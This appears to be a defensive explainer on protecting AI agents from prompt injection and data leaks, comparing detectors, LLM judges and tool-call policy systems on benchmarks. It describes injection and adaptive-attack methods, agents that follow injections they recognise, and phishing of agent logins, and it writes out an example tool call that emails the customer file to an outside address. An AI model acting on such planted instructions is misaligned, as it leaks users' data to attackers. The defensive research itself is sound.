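A redactor occasionally catches a credential by accident. A database address might read "postgres://app:maple7@db.example.com", where "maple7" is the password. A typical pattern for email addresses would match everything from "maple7" onwards and replace it with [EMAIL_1]. The provider wouldn't receive the password, but the company's records would show that the redactor had removed an email address, so nobody would think to change the password. Mishra found a similar problem within a single scanner. When a Google Cloud key ended in a hyphen, the rule for such keys failed and a general entropy rule caught it instead, which lowered the alert from high to medium severity.

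A single engine could still do both jobs, since the basic steps of finding, replacing and restoring values are the same. SlotGuard already handles keys, email addresses and file paths together. But a second list of patterns wouldn't be enough, because the engine has to do different things with what it finds:

| Setting | Credentials | Personal data |
|---|---|---|
| Detection | Prefixes, assignments, and entropy or a tokenizer measure | Patterns, checksums, known customers and a named-entity model |
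| Replacement | A surrogate in the same format, if the agent must use the key | A placeholder is often enough |
| Restoration | Only in a request to the right service | In tool calls and in the reply to the clerk |
| After a find | Cancel and replace the key if anyone may have received it | Nothing comparable |

The restoration setting is probably the easiest to get wrong. The engine should restore Nora Lindqvist's name in the reply before the clerk reads it, but if it restored every value in its table, the clerk could also see the company's API key.

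A specialist scanner's rule list is worth using even inside a shared engine because it helps keep the rules current. Services keep introducing new kinds of key, but Basak and colleagues found one scanner whose rules nobody had updated for well over a year. GitHub rescans old code whenever it adds a new key type. A company that adds three key patterns to its redactor and never updates them will catch those keys, but probably not the kind its next payment provider issues.

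## Whether injection detectors are reliable enough to use

Redaction and credential scrubbing don't remove the planted sentence in the supplier's email, so an injection detector has to catch it. Detectors are easy to adopt because the program only has to run each tool output through a small classifier before the model reads it, with no change to the agent.

### How a detector checks one email

Suppose the supplier's email is long because it quotes weeks of earlier messages. A typical detector would process it like this:

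1. The program splits the email into pieces short enough for the classifier. Prompt Guard 2, the small classifier in Meta's LlamaFirewall, reads 512 tokens at a time, which is a few hundred words.
2. The classifier gives each piece a score from 0 to 1 for how much it resembles an injection.
3. The program uses the highest score for the whole email, so that weeks of pleasantries can't average out one bad paragraph.
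4. It compares that score with a threshold. The default is often 0.5, but a developer can raise it until only 1% of harmless outputs, for example, score above it.
5. If the email scores above the threshold, the program flags it and acts on the flag.

Taking the highest score among the pieces makes false alarms more likely for long texts. If each piece of a harmless email had a 1% chance of a false alarm and the errors were independent, an email of twenty pieces would have an 18% chance. Not splitting long texts is worse. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (Liu, 2026) compared fifteen detectors, and only Meta's three and one called Sheltron split long texts. The other eleven checked only the beginning.

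Liu assumes that the program either drops a flagged output or stops the task and asks a person, but there are milder options. Some tools try to locate the injected passage so that the program can delete it and keep the rest. In Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, a detector adds a warning to the agent's context and passes the text along. A program can also send flagged text to a slower, more accurate check. The choice matters a great deal in the accounts example, because the email that contains the injection also contains the refund amount that the agent needs.

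| Response to a flag | If the email contains an injection | If the alarm is false |
|---|---|---|
| Drop the email | The model never reads the instruction, but it doesn't get the amount either | The agent can't finish the refund |
| Stop and ask the clerk | The clerk decides | The clerk loses time and may take the next alert less seriously |
| Delete the suspicious passage | The model still gets the amount | The agent loses a passage it may need |
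| Add a warning | The model reads the instruction and could still follow it | The agent is more cautious than necessary |
| Run a second check | The second check decides | The company pays for one extra check |

### What a judge can learn from the user's request

A detector can't flag every instruction, because agents need to follow some of them. Dhouib, Elliker and colleagues (2026), in *RAISED*, give the example of a tool output that says "to confirm, enter the code sent to your inbox". An agent changing a password for its user has to follow this instruction. They found that some models trained to resist injections stopped at steps like this one and left the task unfinished.

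*Prompt-Injection Probes Learn the Conversation, Not Just the Injection* (Kale and Vishwanath, 2026) defines an injection as text in a tool output that asks the agent to do something other than what its user requested. Applying that definition requires both the user's request and the tool output, and an LLM judge can read both. Liu gave two language models the request and one tool output, and asked whether the output tried to make the assistant do anything the user hadn't asked for. The score was the probability of "Yes" divided by the combined probability of "Yes" and "No". For example, if the model gave "Yes" a probability of 0.3 and "No" 0.1, the score would be 0.75. A developer could set a threshold on this score, as with any other detector.

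A judge's results depend on the exact question it is given. Liu's question covered actions and tasks. *AgentWatcher* (2026) gives its judge a list of rules that also covers attempts to change the content or format of the agent's answer. It also shows the judge the model's response, whereas Liu's judges saw only the request and the tool output.

### Fifteen detectors on three benchmarks

Liu wanted to know whether a detector's benchmark score predicts how well it works inside an agent. Testing this requires tool outputs known to be harmless and others known to contain an injection. AgentDojo, the benchmark of everyday agent tasks that researchers used to test CaMeL, includes the correct tool calls for each task. Liu ran those calls without a language model or any attack and recorded 339 harmless outputs from 97 tasks.

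Liu then planted attacks in the simulated emails, calendars and bank records, repeated the calls, and labelled an output as injected if it differed from the clean version. An earlier attempt at labelling relied on searching the outputs for the text of the attack. Because AgentDojo inserts line breaks into long text, the search missed every copy of one common attack, and those outputs were labelled as harmless.

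The second benchmark, τ-bench, simulates customer service for a shop and an airline. It has no attacks, so Liu added some to product names, which an outside seller might write. The third, BIPIA, inserts attacks into emails, tables and answers to programming questions.

The table shows seven of the fifteen detectors and both judges. The two false-alarm columns use each detector's default threshold on AgentDojo. The last three columns give the share of injections caught when the threshold allows false alarms on 1% of harmless texts in that benchmark.

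| Detector | Harmless outputs flagged | Tasks with a false alarm | Caught on AgentDojo | Caught on τ-bench | Caught on BIPIA |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| PIGuard | 29.5% | 59.8% | 2.1% | 52.7% | 95.1% |
| ProtectAI v2 | 30.1% | 69.1% | 0.5% | 10.1% | 0.7% |
| Prompt Guard 2 (larger version) | 0.6% | 2.1% | 69.4% | 57.9% | 10.4% |
| Sheltron | 10.6% | 28.9% | 20.1% | 95.2% | 57.2% |
| Prismor | 6.5% | 17.5% | 72.2% | 15.2% | 4.0% |
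| Wolf Defender | 0.9% | 3.1% | 73.8% | 90.8% | 3.5% |
| Horizon-Labs | 0.0% | 0.0% | 82.2% | 100.0% | 37.7% |
| Judge (Qwen2.5-7B) | – | – | 57.4% | 54.3% | 14.9% |
| Judge (Llama-3.1-8B) | – | – | 55.3% | 78.3% | 8.3% |

PIGuard was the best detector on BIPIA but ranked thirteenth of fifteen on AgentDojo. A company that chose it for its BIPIA score would have had almost no protection in an agent like AgentDojo's, unless it accepted far more false alarms. Results differed even between the two agent benchmarks. Prismor did well on AgentDojo but badly on τ-bench, and Sheltron did the reverse.

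Liu measured agreement with Kendall's tau, which is 1 when two rankings are identical and close to 0 when they are unrelated. It was 0.01 between BIPIA and AgentDojo, and 0.28 between AgentDojo and τ-bench. With only fifteen detectors, 0.28 could be chance or a modest real relationship. The rankings by false alarms agreed much better across the two agent benchmarks, at 0.67. A developer can therefore probably use one agent benchmark to rule out detectors that raise too many false alarms, but not to decide which detector will catch the most attacks.

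Horizon-Labs and Wolf Defender did well on both agent benchmarks, so good detection in agents seems possible. All these numbers are somewhat inflated, because Liu picked each threshold on the same harmless texts used in the test. The attacks were also fixed, and Liu did not test commercial detectors.

### Why a good score may not carry over

PIGuard's training data included 1,116 complete inputs from BIPIA. Liu tested it only on attacks that weren't among them, so memorisation alone can't explain its results. But the training inputs contained the same kinds of emails and tables as the test inputs, with attacks inserted in the same way.

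Detectors seem to benefit more from training on the kind of text an attack appears in than from training on the attack itself. PIGuard's training data included 53 of the 62 attacks that Liu used on τ-bench, but only as short prompts. PIGuard caught 52.1% of the tool outputs containing those attacks and 55.8% of the outputs containing the other nine, which were not in its training data.

Horizon-Labs trained its detector on documents and tool responses with planted instructions. Liu searched the five relevant training datasets and found no exact copies of attacks from the three benchmarks. This fits the idea that a detector works best on text in the form it was trained on. *INFUSE* (2026), another benchmark of agent tasks, also found that safety classifiers built for chat do poorly on injections in an agent's environment.

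But the form of the training text can't be the full explanation. Sheltron's developers also trained it on text from agents, yet it caught only 20.1% of injections on AgentDojo. Prompt Guard 2 caught 69.4%, although its documentation mentions no such training. Liu could check the training data of only two detectors, because the other detectors' developers don't publish enough of it.

Kale and Vishwanath found that a detector can also score well without learning much about injections. They studied probes, which read the agent's internal activity instead of the text. In AgentDojo, injections arrive at predictable points in a task and make tool outputs longer, so a simple formula using only position in the conversation and text length did almost as well as the probes on the usual test.

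A further test compared each attack with the same moment of the same task without the injection. At the default threshold, the usual probe flagged a median of 80% of these harmless versions across six models. A different classifier trained on the same data flagged 59%. Adding the harmless versions to its training data, along with harmless notices formatted like attacks, reduced this to 17%. These figures are for applications that appeared in the training data. In new applications there were few false alarms, but the number of attacks the probe caught varied greatly by model.

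### How well the judges did

The two judges caught between 54% and 78% of injections on the agent benchmarks, less than the best dedicated detectors. Both are small models from 2024, so their results are a poor guide to how well a current model could do. The Llama judge's 55.3% on AgentDojo is also very uncertain, with a 95% interval from about 27% to 75%. The judge gave a few harmless outputs high scores, which made the threshold unstable.

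On BIPIA, the Qwen judge caught more than 60% of attacks involving code but only 1% of those that tried to change how the model answered the user's own question. Liu's prompt didn't ask about such changes, and Liu didn't try another wording, so the gap may come from the prompt rather than the model. Only PIGuard, which had been trained on similar text, caught most of the injections that asked for an unrelated, harmless task. It caught 93% of them, the next best detector caught 39%, and no other detector caught more than 20%.

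These results give only limited support for having detectors read more context, because it may help only models that have learned to use it. Sheltron can accept the user's request as an extra input, although its documentation doesn't describe this use. When Liu supplied the request, Sheltron's detection rate on AgentDojo fell from 20.1% to 9.0%, and its false-positive rate on τ-bench rose from 4.4% to 69.7%.

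### How many tasks false alarms would block

PIGuard flagged harmless outputs, including a tool's message that it had updated a password. If the program drops flagged outputs or stops the task, one such mistake can block all the steps that follow.

PIGuard flagged 29.5% of harmless outputs on AgentDojo, where the average task has about 3.5 outputs (339 divided by 97). If its errors were independent, the share of blocked tasks would be:

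1 − (1 − 0.295)^3.5 ≈ 0.71

Liu measured 59.8%. The difference arises partly because some tasks are much shorter than others and partly because false alarms cluster. A detector that mistakes one tool's output format for an injection may flag several outputs in every task that uses the tool, but the first alarm already blocks the task. ProtectAI v2 flagged almost the same share of outputs, 30.1%, but blocked 69.1% of tasks, so its errors were probably less clustered. With only 97 tasks, part of the gap between the two detectors could be chance.

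Horizon-Labs flagged none of the 339 outputs. This is a very good result, but the true false-positive rate could still be as high as about 0.9%. At that rate, more than a third of tasks with fifty outputs would have at least one false alarm. A company with a long-running agent would need to test on many more outputs, preferably its own.

Developers can prevent some false alarms with little effort. In one of Liu's tests, removing the field names from tool outputs cut PIGuard's false-positive rate from 20.0% to 6.7%, and it still caught about as many injections. But PIGuard still performed poorly on AgentDojo, catching only 3.0% of injections with false alarms held to 1%.

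### How many alarms are real

A detector's alarms also depend on how rare injections are. If b is the share of outputs with an injection, d is the share of injections the detector catches and f is its false-positive rate, then:

share of alarms that are real = d × b / (d × b + f × (1 − b))

Suppose the accounts agent uses a detector that catches 82.2% of injections, as Horizon-Labs did on AgentDojo, with a 1% false-positive rate. If one output in a thousand contains an injection, then 100,000 outputs include 100 injections. The detector catches about 82 of them and raises 999 false alarms, so only about 8% of its alarms are real.

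Two large studies suggest how common injections are, and their estimates are far apart. Zhang, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring Real-World Prompt Injection Attacks in LLM-based Resume Screening*, examined nearly 200,000 résumés and found that about 1% contained hidden injections, for example in white text on a white page. Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026), in *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, searched 1.2 billion web addresses for known phrases and confirmed injections on 9,676 pages. That is about eight per million, though a search for known phrases will miss anything worded differently. The same detector would give very different results in these settings:

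| Share of texts with an injection | Share of alarms that are real |
|---|---|
| 1 in 100, as in the résumés | 45% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 8% |
| 8 in 1 million, as on the web pages | 0.07% |

Neither study covers suppliers' emails. The résumé figure is also based on a broad definition of injection. More than 90% of those injections were hidden keywords or invented experience with no explicit instruction, so a detector that looks for instructions could miss most of them. Zhang and colleagues found that general-purpose detectors did poorly on résumés, partly because the injected text makes up so little of a long document. One of their own detectors compares what a person would see on the page with the text a program extracts. An accounts agent that reads PDF invoices could use the same check.

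A high share of false alarms is a serious problem if a clerk has to read every alarm, but it matters much less if an alarm only triggers an automatic second check. In the example with 100,000 outputs, the program would run about 1,080 of these checks, which would take 18 minutes at one second each. The threshold still has to be chosen carefully. Kale and Vishwanath estimate that at the default threshold, the usual probe would send 315,000 of every million outputs for a second check, compared with 74,000 for their improved probe.

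### Injections from live websites

Researchers wrote most of the attacks in these benchmarks, and real attackers may write differently. In *BrowseSafe++*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) built a benchmark mostly from injections on pages that a deployed browser agent had read between September 2025 and September 2026. They kept each injection word for word, rewrote the rest of the page to protect privacy, and paired each page with a clean copy. Of the benchmark's 38,675 pairs, 32,187 use injections from live websites.

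Their collection process also shows how rare real alarms can be. They started with pages that the browser agent's classifier had flagged or that matched certain text patterns. Three language models then examined about 1.09 million of these suspicious pages and, by majority vote, identified an injection on only 58,036, or 5.3%.

Chen and colleagues tested sixteen language models as detectors by giving each a page and a written policy. They also trained BrowseSafe-Guard, a small text detector with 0.8 billion parameters. Each detector read every page as HTML, as Markdown (a simpler text format) and as an accessibility tree, a structured description made for screen readers. The ranges below cover all three formats.

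| Detector | Harmless pages flagged | F1 score |
|---|---|---|
| BrowseSafe-Guard | 1.4–7.4% | 93.0–98.3% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 13.8–15.1% | 91.3–91.6% |
| GPT-5.5 | 19.1–21.2% | 89.0–89.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 21.0–27.6% | 87.4–89.5% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 3.8–4.8% | 84.4–86.5% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 66.9–71.1% | 71.8–73.9% |

The small detector did better overall than far larger frontier models. It cost about 18 cents per thousand pages, compared with $19 to $181 for the frontier models. Opus 5.5 raised fewer false alarms than BrowseSafe-Guard in two of the three formats, but it missed more attacks.

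The small detector probably did better partly because Chen and colleagues trained it on 29,500 pairs from the same collection as the test, much as PIGuard had been trained on BIPIA. Liu's results suggest that it could do much worse on a different kind of text. The larger models received neither this training nor the user's request. Neither Liu nor Chen and colleagues tested a current frontier model that could read both the page and the request, which would be a fairer test of using a model as a judge.

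### Recognising an injection and following it anyway

Chen and colleagues also gave fifteen of the models real tasks on the attacked pages. Models followed an injection in 11,035 cases, and in 74% of these the same model had flagged the page as an attack in the separate detection test. Sonnet 5 both flagged and followed the injection on 19.7% of pages, Opus 5.5 on 15.8%, and GPT-6 Astra on 1.6%.

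"Following" included any movement towards what the injection asked for, such as adopting a requested format or attempting a simulated tool call, so most of these cases probably weren't successful attacks. Many of the pages had been flagged, which isn't surprising because most of the models flag most attacked pages. Even so, a model's ability to recognise an injection clearly doesn't stop it from following one during a task.

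This is a good reason to make detection a separate step, even when the agent's own model is an excellent detector, because a program can act on a flag whatever the agent would have done next. This also raises some doubt about adding a warning and leaving the decision to the agent. A warning in the context might still help a model that hasn't been asked to look for attacks, but Chen and colleagues didn't test that.

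### Attackers who adapt

Adaptive attacks have defeated most of the published detectors that researchers have tested against them. *A Sentence Relation-Based Approach to Sanitizing Malicious Instructions* (2026) points out that these attacks are realistic because detectors often stay the same for a long time and outsiders can query them repeatedly.

Chen and colleagues measured how much a detector still helps by putting BrowseSafe-Guard in front of an agent that used Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite, a small Google model, and replacing every flagged page with a notice. An automated attacker had up to 64 attempts at each of 1,024 tasks, with feedback after each failure.

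| Measure | No detector | With BrowseSafe-Guard |
|---|---|---|
| Original injection succeeds | 4.0% | 1.4% |
| Attack succeeds within 8 attempts | 78.9% | 60.4% |
| Attack succeeds within 64 attempts | 93.6% | 84.2% |
| Agent completes the task when there is no attack | 97.9% | 91.2% |

Narisetty and colleagues would see the third row as the important one, because it supports their view that filters offer no guarantee. Even blocking a page does not always defeat the attack. The detector had blocked the page in 14 of the 862 successful attacks on the protected agent. Some of these succeeded because the attacker's goal was to disrupt the task. For example, a supplier who wanted to delay refunds could benefit if the detector kept the agent from reading an email.

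The first row supports a more favourable view of detectors. The detector blocked 94.5% of the pages with original injections and cut their success rate by about two-thirds. Most attackers may not adapt much. Khodayari and colleagues found that 54 templates accounted for 95% of the injections they confirmed, though their search would have favoured familiar wording. The automated attacker also had unusually good feedback, including a review of what the agent did on each attempt. A malicious supplier could send 64 emails but normally couldn't read the agent's records between them.

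The last row may matter most to a company deciding whether to use a detector. Suppose one task in a thousand contains an ordinary, unadapted injection. Over 100,000 tasks, BrowseSafe-Guard would prevent two or three successful attacks and cause about 6,600 harmless tasks to fail, which is about 2,500 failures for each attack prevented. That many failures could be worthwhile if an attack would empty the company's bank account, but would be far too many for most work. If the program sent flagged pages to a second check instead of blocking them, most of the harmless tasks would probably succeed, and the company would mainly pay for the extra checks.

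## What output validation can still stop

If a planted instruction gets past the detector and the model obeys it, the program receives a tool call that it hasn't yet run. Suppose that, halfway through Nora Lindqvist's refund, the accounts agent proposes this one:

`send_email(to="archive@outside.example", subject="Customer records", attachment="customers.csv")`

No data has left the company at this point. Output validation is the last automatic check that can stop the email, and whether it does depends on what it examines.

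### Four ways to check one email

Form validation compares the call with a schema, which lists the fields a tool accepts and the type of each. The recipient must be an email address, the subject must be text and the attachment must be a file name. This call meets every requirement, so it passes, but passing shows only that the tool can run the call.

Content validation scans the output for credentials, personal data and links. A link in a reply could contain an account number in its web address and send it to an attacker's server when somebody opens the link. If the scan also reads attachments, it will find hundreds of names in the customer file. But a letter to Nora contains her name too, so finding personal data doesn't establish that the recipient shouldn't have it.

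Action validation compares the tool and its arguments with a policy. If the policy lets the agent email only the customer on the order, the program blocks this email without examining its text. The check can still pass an action that the company permits but nobody requested.

An LLM judge compares the proposed call with the user's request. The clerk asked for one refund, so the judge should flag a call that sends out the whole customer file. This check can catch an action that is permitted but that the user didn't want. However, the judge is a model that can be wrong, and the planted text may influence its verdict.

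| Proposed output | Form | Content | Action | Fit with the request |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Customer file emailed to a stranger | Passes | Flags personal data | Blocks the recipient | Probably flags it |
| Refund amount written in words | Blocks | Passes | Depends on the rule | Passes |
| Refund of $840 instead of $84 | Passes | Passes | Blocks it if the order price is the limit | Probably flags it |
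| Email to an approved supplier that hints at another customer's illness | Passes | Probably passes | Passes | May flag it |
| Correct refund to Nora's account | Passes | Flags the account number | Passes | Passes |

### Why a content scan misses reworded values

A pattern describes characters, so it finds a value only if its characters still appear in the same order. Nora's account number, 55208719, no longer matches if the model spells it out in words, encodes it or splits it between two emails. A developer can add a step that undoes common encodings, but nobody can list every way to rewrite a number. Facts are even harder to match because they have no fixed form. The model can rewrite "She was in hospital in March" as "she was unwell in the spring", which contains no name, number or medical term.

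Models reword things without any help from an attacker. In the AgentLeak tests, El Yagoubi and colleagues found models that replaced a diagnosis code with a sentence about what the patient was being treated for, or an exact balance with a remark that it exceeded $50,000. Of the 226 leaks in their breakdown by type, 184 were reworded in this way. They also compared detection methods on 1,000 labelled passages:

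| Method | Leaks caught | Harmless passages flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Search for marker strings planted in the data | 8.0% | 0.0% |
| Markers, plus patterns for items such as card numbers | 18.0% | 0.2% |
| LLM judge | 92.6% | 6.2% |
| All of these together | 93.4% | 4.8% |

The 18% depends on the mix of leaks in the test, most of which were facts about people. Patterns should do much better on API keys, because a paraphrased key is useless to a thief and a model can leak one only by copying it or transforming it reversibly. The judge does far better than patterns on personal facts, but it needs access to the private text and a way to identify which facts are private.

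### Rules for tool calls

A rule about recipients works however the model words the email. Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, built a system that checks every tool call against a list of such rules. Each rule names a tool, allows or forbids it, and can set conditions on its arguments. For Nora's refund, one rule might be:

`allow send_email when to == "nora.lindqvist@example.com"`

Progent checks the "forbid" rules before the "allow" rules and blocks any call that no rule allows. The email to outside.example matches no rule, so Progent blocks it, but the agent can still write to Nora.

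A company can write some rules by hand, such as a ceiling on refunds, and apply them to every task. But the right recipient changes with each request, so Progent has a language model draft the other rules from the request before the agent reads anything untrusted. That draft can turn out to be too narrow. If the clerk asks the agent to do whatever the supplier needs for the return, the policy has to change after the agent reads the supplier's email, which also contains the injection. Progent handles a change like this in several steps:

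1. The drafting model looks at the request and the latest tool call, but not at the tool's result, and decides whether the policy might need an update.
2. If so, it reads the result and drafts a new policy.
3. An SMT solver, a program that can work out whether any values satisfy a set of logical conditions, compares the new policy with the old one.
4. If the new policy allows nothing that the old one blocked, Progent adopts it automatically.
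5. If it allows anything extra, Progent asks for approval, either from a person or from a setting that always says yes or always says no.

An injection may therefore mislead the drafting model, but it can't expand what the agent is allowed to do without approval. On AgentDojo, only 6% of updates needed approval.

In tests with GPT-4o, a model from 2024, Progent cut the success rate of attacks from 39.9% to 1.0% on the agent benchmark AgentDojo and from 70.3% to 3.9% on another, ASB. Shi and colleagues automatically approved every request for extra powers in these tests, to imitate a careless user. When a person reviewed the policies instead, no AgentDojo attack succeeded. Most of the remaining failures on ASB involved malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones, and rules written by hand stopped those too.

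Progent doesn't cover attacks that stay within the permitted actions or harm done by text alone, such as a misleading summary of a supplier's invoice.

### What other teams found

Three other teams have tested Progent. Narisetty and colleagues ran it with a small open model in June 2026. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested it against a stronger adaptive attack, and *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) tested it on harder tasks.

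| Test | Agent's model | Attack success, without and with Progent | Tasks completed, without and with Progent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Shi and colleagues, AgentDojo | GPT-4o | 39.9% → 1.0% | About the same |
| Narisetty and colleagues, part of AgentDojo | Qwen2.5-7B | 25.8% → 4.2% | 45.2% → 27.1%, under attack |
| Ma and colleagues, AgentDojo, adaptive attack | GPT-4o-mini | 52.4% → 7.7% | At most 7 points lower |
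| Li and colleagues, AgentDyn | GPT-4o | 37.8% → 1.7% | 53.3% → 6.7% |

Narisetty and colleagues also wrote an adaptive attack that presented the malicious action as a routine, already authorised step, so that the drafting model would allow it. It succeeded only 2.6% of the time, less often than the standard attack. The softer wording may have made the agent less likely to follow it. If so, the low success rate partly reflects a weak attack.

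Their small test used eight user tasks from each of three applications, and the same 7-billion-parameter model ran the agent and drafted the policies. In one application no attack worked even without Progent, which lowers all the averages. The defended agent also needed about 15 times as many model calls per task. The researchers work for a company that builds security tools of this kind.

Ma and colleagues' result is better evidence of how defenses hold up against a determined attacker. They had Gemini 3.1 Pro, a much stronger model than the agent's, write six successive versions of each injection, and told it only how often each version had worked. Attack success on the same agent rose from zero to 28.0% against PIGuard, one of the detectors in Liu's comparison, and reached 7.7% against Progent. This supports the view that rules on actions withstand adaptive attacks better than detectors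 do.

AgentDyn shows how much a policy can interfere with an agent's task. Its 60 tasks cover shopping, software projects and everyday errands, and each includes a helpful instruction from a third party, such as a request to log in before paying. The agent discovers many of the steps only as it works, whereas just six of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require replanning. Progent reduced the number of tasks completed from 32 to four with GPT-4o and from 31 to 15 with Gemini 2.5 Pro.

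Li and colleagues found that Progent struggled to assign the right permissions when an agent had many tools, and that the mistakes accumulated until it blocked almost everything useful. An AgentDyn task takes about seven steps, so if the mistakes were independent, a fall from 32 completed tasks to four would mean that the policy allowed each necessary step only about 75% of the time. An attack success rate of 1.7% is less impressive when the agent hardly finishes any tasks.

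For an ordinary refund, the company could write most of the policy by hand: refunds go only to the account on record and never exceed the order price, and any emails they trigger go only to the customer or an approved supplier. Open-ended requests are as hard for Progent to handle as they are for CaMeL, and the policy might well stop the agent from completing them.

### When the request is vague

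An LLM judge that checks whether an action fits the user's request has very little to compare the action with when the request is vague. This limits its use for requests that no rule covers, even though it would seem the obvious choice for them.

Ma and colleagues sorted AgentDojo's tasks by how much the user had left open. In the accounts example, "refund Nora $84 for this order" specifies everything, "refund the amount in the supplier's email" leaves one detail open, and "do whatever the supplier needs" leaves the action itself open. With no defence, attacks on GPT-4o-mini succeeded in 87.5% of cases where the action was open, compared with 63.9% and 43.3% for the other two kinds of task. The difference remained when detectors faced adaptive attacks. With PIGuard, these attacks succeeded in 54.2% of cases where the action was open and 17.3% where the user had specified everything.

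Ma and colleagues explain that when a task is vague, an injection doesn't have to look like an instruction, because it can pass as ordinary data about the job. A judge would also have trouble telling the two apart. If the clerk has told the agent to do whatever the supplier needs, an email that says the supplier needs a customer list arguably fits the request.

The most direct evidence on judges comes from DRIFT, which combines a plan and rules with a language model that judges whether instructions conflict with the user's task. The adaptive attack more than doubled attacks' success rate against DRIFT on all three main models, though only from 2.6% to 6.4% on GPT-4o-mini and from 0.3% to 1.5% on Claude Haiku 4.5. DRIFT's rules probably explain much of why these rates are low. Its judge also examines instructions rather than finished tool calls, so a judge that examines tool calls might do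 better or worse.

DRIFT and Progent both kept attack success at or below 11% for every kind of task, including the vague ones. On many of the vague tasks, they did so by limiting the agent to reading, which prevents an attacker from moving money but also blocks the clerk's refund.

### Passwords sent to the wrong site

Phishing is hard for most output checks to catch. Suppose an email asks the accounts agent to log in to a supplier's website to confirm an order, but the link leads to an attacker's copy of the site. Only the destination of the login call is wrong. The call is well formed, it contains a password as it should, and it may even be what the clerk asked for.

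In *CredLeakBench*, Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues (2026) tested seven models on this problem in October 2026. They invented 15 services, gave the agents made-up passwords and personal details, and recorded what the agents submitted. The phishing sites came in eight kinds, including misspelled domains, bare numerical addresses and pages with a certificate warning. The researchers paired every phishing case with a legitimate one, so an agent couldn't do well by refusing to log in anywhere.

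The table shows the share of phishing cases in which each model submitted account information after a user gave it a link and asked it to sign in. In the middle column, the agent was given the official domain and told to compare it with the page. In the last column, it had a tool that made the comparison.

| Model | No guidance | Told to compare domains | Given a checking tool |
|---|---|---|---|
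| Claude Sonnet 5 | 31.2% | 12.5% | 12.5% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 46.9% | 12.0% | 12.5% |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 64.1% | 25.0% | 14.1% |
| GPT-5-mini | 71.9% | 22.4% | 18.8% |
| GPT-5.6-luna | 83.3% | 20.3% | 20.3% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 83.9% | 71.9% | 62.5% |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 86.5% | 54.7% | 39.1% |

Comparing domains also led most models to complete more logins on legitimate sites. GPT-5-mini left 25.0% of these logins undone without guidance, but only 1.6% when it had the official domain. General advice to act safely did little to reduce either leaks or undone logins. When users told the agent to be cautious, leaks fell, but GPT-5-mini left 46.9% of legitimate logins undone.

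The leak rate of the two Claude models seems to have stopped falling at about 12.5%, which is also the share of cases that used the correct hostname over plain HTTP, an unencrypted connection. Across all the sign-in tests, the models leaked in 81% to 94% of those cases, so these cases probably account for nearly all of the Claude models' remaining leaks. The models checked the hostname but not whether the connection was encrypted. Someone on the network could read a password sent this way, but that is less serious than sending it to an impostor.

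All these checks worked only if the model followed the instruction or called the tool. Ordinary code can make the same comparison on every login and release the password only if the connection is encrypted, the certificate is valid and the hostname is identical to the one on record. A credential vault that matches each request to a stored address already does most of this. CredLeakBench didn't test an enforced rule, but such a rule should stop all eight kinds of fake if the recorded address is correct.

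### Outputs that no user reads

Checking only the final reply will miss most leaks in a system of several agents. El Yagoubi and colleagues ran 1,000 tasks from healthcare, finance, law and corporate work on five models from 2024, with one agent coordinating and another doing the work. The runs produced 4,979 usable records.

Private data that the task didn't require appeared in 27.2% of final replies, 46.7% of shared memories and 68.8% of messages between the agents. In 2,076 runs, or 41.7% of the total, the final reply was clean but a message or the shared memory leaked private data. The paper describes this as missing 41.7% of violations, which understates the problem because 41.7% is a share of all runs, including those with no leak. Of the runs that leaked anywhere, about 60% had a clean final reply.

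In a smaller sample of 100 tasks per model, agents did no better with tool calls, passing unnecessary private data to outside tools in 62% to 86% of cases.

These rates are based on a strict definition of a leak. A typical task came with 29 private fields and permission to use three, and one extra field in a message to another agent counted as a leak even though no outsider saw it. The models tested are also old. The comparison between channels is more likely than the rates to hold for current systems, because agents still pass each other the full background to a task.

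The researchers tried several defences on a separate set of tasks that contained no attacks:

| Defence | Final replies that leaked | Messages and memory that leaked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 48% | 31% |
| Privacy instructions in the prompt | 19% | 29% |
| Separate roles for the agents | 22% | 28% |
| Scan that cleans the final reply | 1% | 31% |
| LlamaGuard | 6% | 30% |
| PromptGuard | 8% | 29% |

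The right-hand column barely changes, because the filters ran only on the final reply. PromptGuard detects injections, so it's hard to see why it would prevent so many leaks in tasks without injections. The cleaning scan's near-perfect score is also surprising, given the finding that patterns catch 18% of leaks, unless the scan had a list of the private values to look for.

A prototype that moved the check to messages and memory, and masked private fields there, cut leaks in those channels from 31.5% to 2.4% on 120 tasks. Task completion fell from 78.6% to 73.9%. The prototype had a list of the fields each channel was allowed to carry. Few companies have such a list, and writing one is probably most of the work. When the researchers banned all sharing of private data between agents, only 35% to 65% of tasks succeeded.

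### After a check fires

A program can block the output, repair it, send it back to the model for another try, or ask a person.

Blocking is the safest response, but it leaves the work undone, and agents are bad at finding another way to do it. CredLeakBench included 672 cases in which a phishing message concerned real business, such as an unpaid bill, and the agent could find the genuine site in its records or in an older email. Depending on the model, agents logged in to the genuine site without leaking anything in 0% to 27.7% of cases. GPT-5-mini had the highest rate of the seven models, but it also leaked in 10.4% of cases. Opus 4.8 never leaked, but it never finished the task either. It nearly always escalated the problem, which an accounts department might prefer.

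GPT-5-mini recovered more than twice as often when its records contained the full login address (38.1%) as when an old email contained only the domain (17.3%). A check that blocks a login could therefore also return the correct address.

Repairing the output works for small formatting errors, such as a date in the wrong order, and for private details in a log or an internal message. It is a poor response to a bad action. If the program masked the account numbers in the customer file but sent the file to the stranger anyway, the attacker would still get the names.

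When Progent blocks a call, it lets the model try again by default. It returns a message that explains the block and repeats the user's task, so that the agent can carry on with the refund. This is fairly safe with a fixed rule, because every attempt has to pass the same rule. Retries are riskier with an LLM judge. If the judge misses one bad call in ten and its errors are independent, the chance that at least one of five bad calls gets through is 41%. A limit of one or two retries makes sense with an LLM judge.

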